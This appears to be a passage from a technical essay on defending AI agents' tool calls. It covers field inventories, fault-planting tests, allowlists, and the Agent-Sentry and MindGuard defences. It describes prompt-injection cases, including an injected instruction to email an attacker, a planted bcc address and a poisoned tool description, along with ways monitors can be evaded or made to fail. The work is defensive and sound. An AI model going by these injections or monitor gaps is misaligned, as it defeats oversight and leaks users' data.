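Showing a language model judge a full email address takes little compute, but showing it a full attachment can take a lot, and the judge would get little useful information from a file in base64. It is better for ordinary software to decode the file, scan it for sensitive data, and give the judge the file's name, real type, size and origin. Every field then gets a suitable check without any single model having to read everything, and the judge receives less private data.

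Labelling the arguments as data may help against hostile text in them, but it doesn't guarantee that the judge will ignore instructions there. Fixed checks on recipients and paths should therefore run separately, so that they can still block an email if hostile text leads the judge to approve it.

Blocking on errors has a large hidden cost when sessions are long. Suppose that the monitor fails on 1% of calls and that failures are independent. The chance that a session of 200 calls has at least one interruption is:

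```
1 − 0.99^200 ≈ 0.87
```

An attacker could also cause interruptions on purpose, for example by planting text that makes a tool call's argument too long to review. It seems sensible to block on errors when a call sends data, spends money or deletes something, and to let most lookups inside a sandbox continue. A web request shouldn't count as a harmless lookup, since its URL can carry data out.

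### Listing fields and reporting cuts

A field inventory lists every part of an action and what the monitoring system does with it. For an email tool, the inventory might record that a rule checks the recipients, a judge reads the body, a scanner opens the attachments, and nothing checks the declared file type. The last entry is the most useful because it lets the company find a gap before an attacker does.

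Software can build much of the inventory from the schema, the part of a tool's definition that lists its arguments. It can then hold any call with an argument missing from the inventory, which would stop a tool update from adding an unchecked "htmlBody". However, the schema doesn't list headers that the client adds or changes that the tool makes later, so somebody has to trace those by hand. The main burden is keeping the inventory current, which might be difficult for a company with hundreds of frequently changing tools.

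An inventory contains no customer data and raises no false alarms by itself, but holding calls with unknown arguments will delay some legitimate ones after an update. Publishing the full inventory would show attackers which fields nobody checks, so a company could give that version to its auditors and customers and publish a shorter one.

Reporting truncation is simpler still. Whenever the software shortens or drops a field, it adds a line such as:

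```
body: 512 of 5,000 characters shown; attachments: omitted
```

A notice that counts the missing tool calls uses a few tokens and reveals almost nothing private. It would have immediately exposed the 53 blank steps in the evaluation pipeline that Xia and colleagues examined. But a language-model judge might read the notice and approve the action anyway. For risky actions, the software should return "incomplete" instead of a verdict, then either fetch the missing calls or ask a person.

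### How many planted faults are enough

An inventory shows that a field reaches the monitor, but only a test can show that the monitor reacts to it. The tester can plant faults in one field at a time and measure paired discrimination for each field.

Suppose the monitor catches all *n* faults that the tester planted in a field. Its true miss rate could still be above zero. The upper end of the 95% interval is the miss rate at which *n* catches in a row would have a probability of only 2.5%:

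```
(1 − m)^n = 0.025
m = 1 − 0.025^(1/n)
```

For *n* = 100, the upper limit *m* is about 3.6%, and a single miss would raise it to about 5.4%. A tool with 20 fields would need 2,000 faulty runs to reach the 3.6% limit for each field separately. Getting the limit below 1% with no misses would take 368 faulty runs per field, or 7,360 for 20 fields.

Each interval applies to only one field, so with 20 intervals there is a greater chance that at least one is wrong. With 100 runs per field, a standard correction raises the limit from 3.6% to 6.5%. Getting it back to 3.6% takes about 180 runs per field, or 3,600 in all.

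Clean runs add less to the total because one clean run can be reused to create a fault in every field. A test with 100 clean runs and 2,000 faulty ones needs 2,100 reviews. These would cost about $7 with GLM-5.2 and $20 with Claude Opus 4.8, at the prices Caldwell and colleagues reported for judges that receive the user's request and earlier calls. Most companies could afford to run the test weekly.

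Producing good faults is harder. A hundred bcc addresses at obviously hostile domains would test little more than one such address, and the same is true of 100 copies of one misleading filename. A thorough test of the bcc field would include lookalike domains, former employees and real colleagues who shouldn't receive the message. Testing 20 fields with five types of fault each, and 100 runs per type, would take 10,000 faulty runs.

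The result also holds only for faults like those in the test, while an attacker will look for others. And it can go out of date when the company changes the model, the prompt or the software that prepares the monitor's input. The company could run a smaller test, with perhaps ten faults per field, after every change. With no misses, the upper limit on the miss rate is about 31%, so this test would reliably reveal only a large failure, such as a field that no longer reaches the monitor.

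Testers can use invented people and files, which avoids most privacy problems. They should run the tests without sending anything, since a monitor that misses a planted address would otherwise let a real email go out.

### Leaving the agent fewer ways to cause harm

Some protections work even if a monitor detects nothing. For example, a destination allowlist lets an agent send data only to approved addresses or domains. It takes almost no resources to run, and hostile text can't change which destinations it allows. It raises false alarms for legitimate new contacts. It also fails when an approved destination is the wrong one for the task, or when an attacker controls an account on an approved service.

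Narrow argument formats remove options that the agent doesn't need. The schema below is for an invented email tool that can write only to contacts the company has already entered:

```json
{
  "type": "object",
  "properties": {
    "contact": { "type": "string", "enum": ["maria", "jonas"] },
    "subject": { "type": "string", "maxLength": 120 },
    "body":    { "type": "string", "maxLength": 5000 }
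  },
  "required": ["contact", "subject", "body"],
  "additionalProperties": false
}
```

A properly built server would reject a call with a "bcc" argument because it violates this schema. The last line is important because a schema normally accepts arguments it doesn't list. The length limits also let a monitor read every call in full. The drawback is that a user who needs a blind copy would have to send that email by hand.

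Fetch tools should also restrict headers in both directions. Without giving the monitor more to read, they can drop unneeded response headers, as trackr.live recommends, and stop the agent from setting its own request headers, which could otherwise carry private data out.

### Agent-Sentry: checking where a value came from

An allowlist checks only the value, but the same value can be right in one task and wrong in another. *Agent-Sentry* gives the example of lily.white@gmail.com. In some test tasks, the user asks the agent to email Lily. In others, the user only wants to delete a calendar event, but an injected instruction tells the agent to send Lily an attacker's message. The allowlist must include her address for the legitimate tasks to work, which also lets the attack through.

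Agent-Sentry therefore has the agent report the source of each argument value and checks some of these reports against the source's text. It then reviews each action in up to three layers:

1. A classifier or a set of rules looks at the order of the tool calls and the sources of their arguments. It doesn't interpret the text that the agent read, so persuasive wording can't influence it. It allows the action, blocks it or passes it on.
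2. For unclear actions, a fixed check compares recipients, account numbers and similar values with those in earlier legitimate runs. It allows the action if the values are known and came from trusted sources.
3. A language-model judge decides the remaining cases. It receives the user's request, the call, recent calls, the source of each argument, and short extracts from any untrusted text that supplied a value.

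In the Lily example, the address came from an untrusted source, so the first two layers pass the action on to the judge. The judge finds no request to email anyone and blocks the action.

The researchers compared Agent-Sentry with Progent, which enforces hand-written rules, and CaMeL, which separates planning from the handling of untrusted text. One test set was their own 5,380 runs, and the other was 670 runs from two existing benchmarks, AgentDojo and AgentDyn. Each cell gives the share of attacked runs the system blocked, then the share of harmless runs it blocked.

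| System | Own test set | Existing benchmarks | Time per run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-Sentry, classifier | 96.8% / 3.6% | 91.2% / 30.9% | 4.3 s |
| Agent-Sentry, rules | 95.3% / 10.7% | 93.2% / 12.9% | 5.5 s |
| Progent | 97.7% / 30.8% | 88.4% / 6.3% | 4.3 s |
| CaMeL | Not tested | 99.3% / 69.0% | 26.6 s |

The Agent-Sentry figures come from runs that the researchers didn't use to fit the system. The better figures in the paper's abstract, 94.3% of attacks blocked and 4.9% of harmless runs stopped, come from rules fitted and tested on the same runs, so those figures aren't a good guide to performance on new tasks.

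False alarms rose on the existing benchmarks partly because users there typically ask the agent to read a file and pay the bill in it. The correct account number therefore comes from an untrusted file, just as an attacker's would. The classifier was also hard to train because there were only 126 harmless runs. When the researchers fitted the system only on their own test set and then ran it on the benchmarks, the classifier stopped 35.6% of harmless runs and the rules stopped 20.9%.

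Even blocking 3.6% of harmless runs could be a heavy burden. If 10 of 10,000 runs were under attack, the classifier version would likely block nearly all 10, along with about 360 harmless runs. A company would probably want to ask the user about flagged actions rather than block them outright.

The judge alone did almost as well. With a carefully tuned prompt, it blocked 95.4% of attacks and stopped 2.0% of harmless runs on the researchers' own test set. With an untuned prompt, it blocked 75.5% and stopped 18.0%. In the classifier version, only 3.1% of actions reached the judge, which reduced the average delay per run from 2.4 seconds to 0.07 seconds. The earlier layers make the system faster and less dependent on the prompt, but don't clearly make it more accurate than a well-tuned judge.

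Agent-Sentry's list of known values leaves out URLs and message bodies because they change often. An unclear call with a known recipient and a hostile URL could therefore pass the second layer without reaching the judge. The rules version also allows any action that no rule matches, which is the opposite of blocking on error.

The system also relies on the agent to report where values came from, and a hijacked agent could report this falsely. Checking the reports against the source text catches some false ones but not all. Knowing a value's source also doesn't help when the user has asked the agent to rely on that source. For example, a fake invoice that looks exactly like a real one can supply the attacker's account number where the genuine one belongs.

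### MindGuard: poisoned tool descriptions

A tool's description can influence an agent even if the agent never calls that tool. For example, the description of a harmless-looking tool could tell the agent to change the recipient whenever it sends an email. A record of the calls would show only the email tool and its arguments. *MINDGUARD* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2025) looks for this influence inside the model.

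MindGuard uses attention, the numerical weights with which a language model draws on earlier parts of its input as it writes. It first removes words that attract a lot of attention regardless of their meaning. It then adds up the squared attention weights between each part of the input and the new call, and treats the total as that part's influence. For each tool that the agent didn't call, it computes:

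```
ratio = influence of the uncalled tool's description
        ÷ (influence of the user's request
           + influence of the called tool's description)
```

If the uncalled tool scores 0.6, the request 0.3 and the called tool 0.2, the ratio is 0.6 / 0.5 = 1.2. MindGuard treats a ratio above a chosen threshold as a sign of poisoning and flags the tool with that ratio as the suspected source. It measures a tool's influence on the arguments separately from its influence on the choice of tool, because copying a value such as an address into the arguments produces a much stronger signal that could hide the influence on the choice.

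With the Qwen3-8B model and a threshold of 0.9, MindGuard caught 91.2% of poisoned calls, or 62 of 68. It raised no false alarms on 479 calls without a poisoned description, and flagged 0.9% of calls where a poisoned description was present but hadn't affected the call. Lowering the threshold to 0.5 raised recall to 97.1%, but the false-alarm rates rose to 1.5% and 13.1%, respectively.

MindGuard's AUROC ranged from 0.91 to 0.99 across seven model set-ups when the negative cases also contained poisoned descriptions. It identified the right tool in at least 95% of the attacks it detected. It added less than a second of delay and needed no extra model calls.

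The approach helps privacy because whoever runs the model can apply it without sending the data to another company. It also doesn't read the description as instructions, so an attacker can't manipulate it by writing instructions there. An attacker might still find wording that changes the call while attracting little attention. Wang and colleagues think this would be difficult but don't prove it's impossible.

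MindGuard needs attention weights, which customers of closed models normally can't see, so only the model's provider could use it on those models. The tests used small open models of up to about 14 billion parameters. The ratio covers only uncalled tools, so it wouldn't flag a poisoned description of the tool that the agent does call, an instruction in a web page, or a server that changes the email after receiving it.

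### The bcc email again

For the agenda email to Maria, the strongest design combines restrictions, fixed checks and a judge, with each handling the fields it suits.

The simplest restriction is to give the agent an email tool without a "bcc" argument. If users need blind copies, software should check every recipient in the To, Cc and Bcc fields. Maria's address passes because the user named her and the address comes from the company's directory. The planted address, archive@example.net, appears in neither the request nor the directory, so the software blocks the call without relying on a model or person to notice the address.

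A directory check alone would miss a planted address that belonged to a real colleague, as in the Lily example. When a call includes a colleague the user didn't mention, the software should pass the complete call and the user's request to a judge. The judge then only has to decide whether the request gives any reason to include this person.

The attachment needs its own checks because Maria, though a permitted recipient, could still receive a payroll file by mistake. The software can require the agent to refer to a stored file instead of supplying its content, which prevents the agent from sending a payroll file under the name "agenda.pdf". The software can then scan the file and hold the email if the file contains salary data or the user didn't ask for it.

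None of these checks would catch an address that the tool adds afterwards. To catch that, the company has to compare the recipients in the approved call with those in the message actually sent. It can automate this if the tool sends mail through a server the company controls. If an outside service sends the mail, the company may learn of the extra recipient only from that service's logs.

Testing this design takes less work than testing a judge that checks every field. The example call has seven fields: the recipient, bcc address, subject, body, filename, file type and content. A judge responsible for all seven would need 700 faulty emails to reach the 3.6% limit on each. A fixed recipient rule always gives the same result for the same address, so its developers can test the difficult cases, such as lookalike domains and addresses in unusual formats, and keep the large samples for the fields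 the judge checks.

Recipients are hard to check when a user asks the agent to copy in everyone from an email thread. Even the correct addresses then come from messages that outsiders may have written, and those messages could also contain an attacker's address. The software can list every recipient with the source of the address and highlight those outside the company, but a person still has to read the list.
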